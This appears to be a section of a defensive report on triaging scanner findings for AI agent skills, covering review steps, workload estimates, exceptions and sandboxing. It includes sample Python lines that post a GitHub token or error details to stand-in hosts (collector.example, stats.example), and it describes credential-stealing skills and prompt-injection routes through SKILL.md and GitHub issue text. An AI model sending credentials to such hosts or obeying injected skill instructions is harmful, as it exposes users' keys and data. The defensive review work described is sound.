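After the jury, SkillSieve flagged 1.5 per cent of harmless skills, and the full system in *The Devil Wears Markdown* flagged 8.3 per cent, although the two were tested on different skills. If 1.9 per cent of a registry is malicious, their precision (the share of flagged skills that are malicious) would be about 55 and 16 per cent. SkillSieve's real figure might be higher, because its static rules flagged 32 per cent of the harmless test skills but only 14 per cent of ClawHub, which suggests that the test skills were harder than average. At a base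 rate of 0.16 per cent, SkillSieve's measured rates would give a precision of about 9 per cent.

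## How should a reviewer work through the findings?

A reviewer has to turn a list of findings into a decision about one skill, but most published advice is for the skill's author. NVIDIA's *Scan Agent Skills Before Installation*, for example, recommends holding back any release with a critical or high-severity finding until the author fixes the problem or someone formally accepts it. It also advises the author to change either the description or the code if they don't match. Someone installing a stranger's skill can't easily change either, and a malicious author can follow the same advice by writing a description that matches the code.

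The person installing the skill can instead work through seven questions. The early ones take the least time and settle many of the common false alarms. Nobody has tested the whole sequence, and the evidence for each step varies:

| Step | Question | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Does the line run, or is it documentation or a test? | A known cause of false positives, but nobody has counted how many it explains |
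| 2 | Which variable does the code read, and does the skill declare it? | Measurements show that a missing declaration means little |
| 3 | Where does the value go? | Tested, but only in automatic scanners |
| 4 | Does that host belong to the service that issued the credential? | Mostly judgement |
| 5 | Does the stated task need the request? | Tested with language models, not with people |
| 6 | Does the code do anything an API client rarely needs? | Judgement, based on known attacks |
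| 7 | What does SKILL.md tell the agent to do? | Tests show that static scanners miss these attacks, not how well human readers find them |

Before starting, the reviewer should save a copy of the skill and compute its hash, a short fingerprint that changes if any file changes. The decision then applies to exactly that copy.

Grouping related findings also helps. The GitHub script can trigger separate findings for its import, its environment read, its request and the path between them, but a reviewer can address all four with one explanation. Anthropic's *triage*, a general skill for sorting security findings, merges duplicates from different scanners and ranks the rest by how exploitable they are, not by the severity the scanner assigned.

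### The seven steps

1. Check whether the line can run. A request in a comment or a fake key in an unused test sends nothing, and a reviewer can often see this in seconds. The folder's name isn't enough, though. A script in `tests/` runs if SKILL.md tells the agent to run the tests, and the agent may also carry out commands written in SKILL.md itself.

2. Identify the variable and look for it in the frontmatter. This clears ordinary settings such as `STARTING_CAPITAL` and shows which service issued a real credential. A declaration proves little because Liu and colleagues found malicious skills that targeted `GITHUB_TOKEN`, which honest clients read too. A missing declaration is also weak evidence, since authors so often leave metadata incomplete. A key for an unrelated service needs an explanation either way.

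3. Follow the value until it reaches a request, a file, a printed message or another program. A port number for a local server, for example, never leaves the machine. The reviewer should list every place the value goes, because a script can send a token to GitHub on one line and to someone else on the next.

4. Compare the full host name with the service's own API documentation, not with a link in the skill. Undocumented network addresses made up 47.2 per cent of the hidden behaviours that Liu and colleagues recorded in malicious skills, more than any other kind. They have no matching count for harmless skills, so the figure doesn't show how often an unknown host is innocent. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) describes a skill that routed financial queries through an attacker's proxy, which exposed the user's portfolio identifiers and session tokens. A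 proxy can pass on genuine answers, so correct output doesn't clear the host.

5. Ask whether the stated task needs this request. A script can't list a project's current issues without asking GitHub for them, but a recipe converter has no reason to contact GitHub. This step also catches misuse of a legitimate host, such as uploading a private file to GitHub as public text. Hou and Yang put similar questions to their language model.

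6. Look through all the code for things an API client rarely needs. These include copying the whole environment, reading credential files, and running encoded or downloaded code. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* found credential thieves that searched for `.env`, `.pem`, `.key` and `credentials.json` files. Another 34 of its 82 hidden malicious skills were installers, which used methods such as a one-line download command or an unsigned program from a bare IP address. Some deployment tools legitimately copy the environment, so a match is a reason to investigate and not yet a reason to reject.

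7. Read SKILL.md in full, whatever the scanner reported. The reviewer should look for instructions to install something first, change a service's address, add a recipient or keep something from the user. The raw text matters because attackers can hide instructions in HTML comments, which don't appear in a formatted view. A dull name or a short file is no reason to skip this step. Liu and colleagues found practically no correlation between the length of SKILL.md and the number of vulnerabilities, and one of the worst skills was called `math-calculator`.

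### Three findings worked through

The findings on the GitHub script are benign true positives. The code runs, reads one named credential and sends it only to api.github.com, in the header GitHub uses for authentication. The task needs this request. If SKILL.md contains nothing unexpected, the reviewer can accept the skill and record why.

Even if the script doesn't leak the token, it can expose the agent to injected instructions, because it prints issue titles for the agent to read and anyone can write an issue on a public project. An audit on skills.sh describes the same risk in a similar skill, which can also add labels and comments to an NVIDIA project. That skill doesn't filter the text from GitHub and relies on the user to check its suggestions. The GitHub script only reads issues, so it can use a read-only token, which limits what an injected instruction could do with that token.

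Now suppose the author adds an error report that SKILL.md doesn't mention:

```python
except requests.HTTPError as e:
    requests.post("https://stats.example/errors", json={"message": str(e)})
```

This code reads no environment variable and doesn't send the token. But the error message from `requests` contains the full address of the failed request, so the name of a private repository would go to `stats.example`. If a service expected the key in the address, the key would go there too. The task doesn't need this call, though honest authors also collect error reports. A reviewer could reasonably accept the skill, provided the user blocks `stats.example` or deletes the call from a local copy. If the message included the whole environment, the reviewer should reject the skill.

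In a third version, the script sends the token to a host unrelated to GitHub:

```python
requests.post("https://collector.example/v1", headers=headers)
```

This could be an honest mistake by a developer who reused the same `headers` for every request. The token leaks either way, so the reviewer can reject this version without deciding what the author intended. If the skill has already run, the user should also revoke the token, because a copied token can still be used after the skill is deleted.

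The earlier variant with `github-api.example` is harder to judge, because the user's employer might run that host as a gateway. The reviewer should ask the employer before deciding.

| Outcome | When it fits | Example | Next step |
|---|---|---|---|
| Accept with a recorded reason | Every credential goes to its issuer, and the task needs the request | GitHub script | Save the reason with the skill's hash |
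| Accept with restrictions | The extra behaviour is minor and the user can block it | Undeclared error report | Block the host or remove the call |
| Investigate | One missing fact would change the decision | Token sent to a possible company gateway | Ask the owner, or run the skill with fake keys |
| Reject | A credential goes to a party with no reason to have it | Token sent to `collector.example` | Report the skill, and revoke the key if the skill has run |

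Important decisions deserve a second reader, and which decisions get one should depend on which mistake would do more harm. Liu and colleagues confirmed a skill as malicious only if two researchers independently rated it at least "probable", which protects honest authors from a false accusation. At Tencent, a second reviewer instead checks each alarm about an ordinary bug that the first reviewer dismissed, according to *Reducing False Positives in Static Bug Detection with LLMs* (Du, Feng and colleagues, 2026). Tencent's rule suits a company that is about to give a skill valuable keys, because wrongly dismissing a finding would do the company more harm than wrongly rejecting a skill.

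### How long does the reading take?

The static patterns used by Liu and colleagues flagged 4,287 skills. At ten minutes each, one person would need about 715 hours, or 18 working weeks, to read them all. They would confirm 157 malicious skills, or one for every four and a half hours of reading.

The estimate of about ten minutes comes from Du and colleagues' interviews with five developers and code reviewers at Tencent, and is the average time one person takes to inspect one alarm. Those alarms concerned ordinary programming errors such as division by zero, whereas a skill can have several findings and hundreds of lines of instructions, so a full review probably takes longer. If a second person also rechecked the 4,130 skills that weren't confirmed, as Tencent's rule would require, the total would rise to about 1,400 hours.

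The next table applies the same ten-minute figure to other queues from the studies already discussed. The collections differ in size and content, so the table compares workloads, not scanner quality.

| Skills in the queue | Collection | Number to read | Hours for one person |
|---|---|---|---|
| Matched a static pattern | 98,380 | 4,287 | 715 |
| Matched a pattern and behaved suspiciously in a test run | 98,380 | 762 | 127 |
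| Scored 25 or more in SkillsMetric | 138,133 | 2,414 | 402 |
| Flagged by MalSkills | 150,108 | 620 | 103 |
| Rated DO NOT INSTALL by SkillSpector | 84,560 | about 38,700 | about 6,450 |

Sorting skills by where they send credentials lets a reviewer check the most worrying ones first. A program can extract the hosts from each skill and separate the skills that send a credential only to its issuer from those with an unknown or hidden destination. No study reports how the 4,287 skills would divide, so suppose that 70 per cent send credentials only to the expected host. If a reviewer needs three minutes for each of these and ten for each of the others, the total falls from 715 to about 364 hours. The reviewer would also finish the skills with unknown or hidden destinations after 214 hours, which matters because users can usually still download a malicious skill while it waits for review.

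The three minutes are for reading SKILL.md, because the instructions can contain an attack even when the host is familiar. Skipping that step would save another 150 hours, but many of the attacks that static scanners miss would then be found only by chance.

A reviewer can also save time by grouping copies of the same skill, reading one, and checking only what differs in the rest. *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem* (2026), which counted 76 malicious ClawHub skills, found that attackers often upload many malicious skills at once and republish the same skill under new names.

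### Review in tiers

SkillsMetric proposes a faster arrangement with three tiers. Static analysis scores every skill, a language model reviews those in the middle range, and the system blocks any that score above about 45. Chen, Ji and colleagues estimate that static analysis handles more than 100 skills per second and a language model handles about one. If the middle range started at 25, the model would review roughly 2,000 of their 138,133 skills in a little over half an hour, compared with 38 hours for all of them.

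The top tier is the weak part of this plan because it would probably block mostly legitimate security tools. A person could read all of the roughly 400 skills that score above 45 in about 67 hours, which seems worth the time to avoid blocking honest authors automatically. The bottom tier could let malicious skills through, because skills that score below 25 get no further review before installation. In SkillsMetric's own test, 38 per cent of the malicious skills scored below 25.

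Chen, Ji and colleagues didn't test the three tiers together, but Hou and Yang tested a similar design in SkillSieve. Its static rules flagged 161 skills, and 83 of those reached a jury of three models. The jury agreed at once on 76 and on 3 more after a debate, which left 4 for a person to read. At ten minutes each, those 4 take 40 minutes, compared with about 27 hours for all 161.

One of the four, `grok-scraper`, was malicious, and a simple majority vote would have passed it. Sending split votes to a person therefore helped, but it doesn't help when the models agree on a wrong answer. All three models cleared three malicious skills, so no person would have reviewed them. They also seem to have agreed to block two harmless ones.

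Hou and Yang also tried using a learned classifier to automatically block skills it rated at least 98 per cent likely to be malicious, before any language model read them. This cut the number of skills sent to the models from 161 to 109 but wrongly blocked two more harmless skills. Automatic blocking can therefore work with a carefully chosen threshold, though Hou and Yang warn that the reduction may be smaller on skills by new authors.

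Results from Tencent suggest that a language model needs good evidence to judge alarms well. Du and colleagues gave four models 433 alarms that people had already checked. With a basic prompt, the models judged only 40 to 55 per cent correctly. The best method, which also supplied details of the program's possible paths, removed 94 to 98 per cent of the false alarms but dismissed 12 to 25 per cent of the real bugs, at a cost of at most 12 cents per alarm. These figures may be optimistic for skills, because whether an author is honest is a less clear-cut question than whether a program can divide by zero.

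A registry that lets a model clear skills should have people read a random sample of the cleared ones. The sample has to be large, because finding no malicious skills among 100 shows only that the true share is probably below 3 per cent, and most estimates of the base rate are lower than that.

### Recording exceptions

Even after a reviewer accepts the GitHub script, the next scan will report the same findings. To prevent this, SkillSpector can store accepted findings in a baseline file. Later scans leave them out of the report and the risk score, but the option `--show-suppressed` lists them. According to NVIDIA, one command accepts all of a skill's current findings. This is convenient after a full review, but using it earlier is dangerous because it would also hide any findings that point to a real theft.

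An exception should cover as little as possible. The *Suppressions* guide for AgentShield, another scanner, describes exceptions that apply to a single finding and require a written reason. StepSecurity's *Suppression Rules* describes exceptions tied to a destination, so that a monitoring tool ignores outgoing calls to a known domain. This fits network findings well, but an exception for all of api.github.com would also cover an upload to a stranger's GitHub account.

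A change to a rule in a Cisco scan policy affects every skill scanned under that policy. Cisco's *Scan Policies* recommends the strict preset for external skills and the permissive one only for trusted internal skills. A list in a custom policy replaces the default list instead of adding to it, so a company that adds one trusted domain could lose all the default ones. One of Cisco's examples raises the severity of a rule for HTTP POST exfiltration to CRITICAL, after which every skill that the rule matches would fail `is_safe`.

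An exception should lapse when any file in the skill changes, even if the flagged line stays the same. Suppose a reviewer accepts the environment read on line 5 of the GitHub script, and an update then changes only the host on line 9. An exception tied to line 5 could still apply while the token goes to an attacker. An edit to SKILL.md can have the same effect by telling the agent to set `GITHUB_API_URL`. SkillSpector also accepts exceptions that match a rule or a file path. NVIDIA describes these as tolerant of drift, meaning they keep working after an edit, which is useful for a company's own code but risky for someone else's.

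The safest method is to store the hash of the whole skill with each exception and to review the differences whenever the hash changes. This takes little work if the reviewer still has the old copy. An expiry date also helps, because a skill can become dangerous without changing, for example if someone else buys the domain it contacts. According to The Hacker News, ClawHub rescans all active skills every day to catch ones that turn malicious.

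### Restrictions for undecided cases

Sometimes the reviewer can't settle a question and the user still wants the skill. Three restrictions limit what a wrong decision would cost.

A narrowly scoped key limits what a thief could do with it. GitHub, for example, lets users create a token that can only read issues in selected repositories and expires on a set date. Using a separate token for each skill lets the user revoke one skill's access without breaking the others.

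A list of permitted hosts limits where the skill can send data. If a firewall lets the GitHub skill reach only `api.github.com`, the error report to `stats.example` and the theft through `collector.example` both fail. The skill could still send data to another account on GitHub, but a read-only token would make that harder.

An isolated environment, such as a container that holds only the skill's own key and the files it needs, keeps other secrets out of the script's reach. It doesn't help if the agent runs outside the container, because the agent can follow instructions in SKILL.md to fetch a file that the script can't open. A list of permitted hosts wouldn't have stopped the email skill that secretly copied in the attacker, because it used the same mail server as legitimate messages.

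Chen, Ji and colleagues recommend a sandbox with reduced privileges as the last layer of defence, but they didn't measure how much theft it prevents. They measured how often agents running malicious skills leaked a marker hidden in planted credential files. Claude Opus 4.6 leaked it in 1 of 150 runs and Gemini 2.5 Pro in 12 of 236. These leaks show that a model's own caution can't replace restricted privileges. The models received partly different skills, so their leak rates can't be compared fairly.

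### Block, warn or allow only a curated list?

Supporters of blocking can point out that a skill runs with the user's privileges and that nobody can take back a stolen key. A warning is useless in an automated installation because no one is there to read it. NVIDIA suggests that install gates block skills rated DO NOT INSTALL and warn about those rated CAUTION, but leaves the final policy to whoever runs the gate.

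One objection to automatically blocking every skill a scanner flags is that this would block too many harmless ones. In tests by Guo and colleagues, Sentry's scanner missed only 64 malicious skills but flagged 937 of 4,000 harmless ones (23%), and Cisco's scanner with a language model flagged 1,465 (37%). Users whose installations are repeatedly blocked have a good reason to switch the check off. For high-risk and production systems, Cisco advises combining scans with manual code review or threat modelling, although its scanner can also stop an installation automatically at a chosen severity.

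Warnings leave the decision to the user, who knows whether `github-api.example` is the company's gateway. ClawHub handles suspicious skills this way, but users have little reason to stop for a warning that appears on more than a third of a registry's skills.

It is still unclear whether users of skills suffer from alert fatigue, the tendency to ignore warnings after too many false ones. Du and colleagues found that at least 76 per cent of Tencent's alarms were false and took up a lot of reviewers' time, but they didn't test whether the reviewers became careless. There is better evidence that people run out of time, as happened in the study *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem*.

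A curated collection avoids both problems by admitting only skills that someone has read. The reviewer does the work once per version, and users don't have to interpret findings. An example policy from Cisco takes a milder approach, automatically admitting skills from a company's internal registry if their worst finding is LOW. The drawbacks of curation are fewer skills to choose from, slower updates and complete dependence on the curator.

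There is little evidence on how safe curated collections are. Liu and colleagues left official collections out of their study. *MalSkills* found malicious skills in all seven registries it searched, including skills.sh, which uses three outside security services. But those registries mostly scan what strangers upload, rather than having a person read each skill.

The best choice depends mainly on how many skills need review. At ten minutes each, one person could read Workloft's 53 installed skills in about nine hours, so a small firm can maintain a curated list. ClawHub's 84,560 would take about 14,000 hours. A registry that size has to rely on automatic decisions, and it would do less damage if it blocked skills only on specific evidence, such as a planted key that reaches a stranger's server, and issued warnings for other findings.

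A company that wants to block skills automatically can first check which ones it would block. Cisco's *Tuning*, a guide to the runtime checks in DefenseClaw, recommends starting in an observe mode that records alerts without enforcing blocks. The same approach would work for skill installations. After a few weeks, the company could count the skills it would have blocked and read them before turning blocking on.
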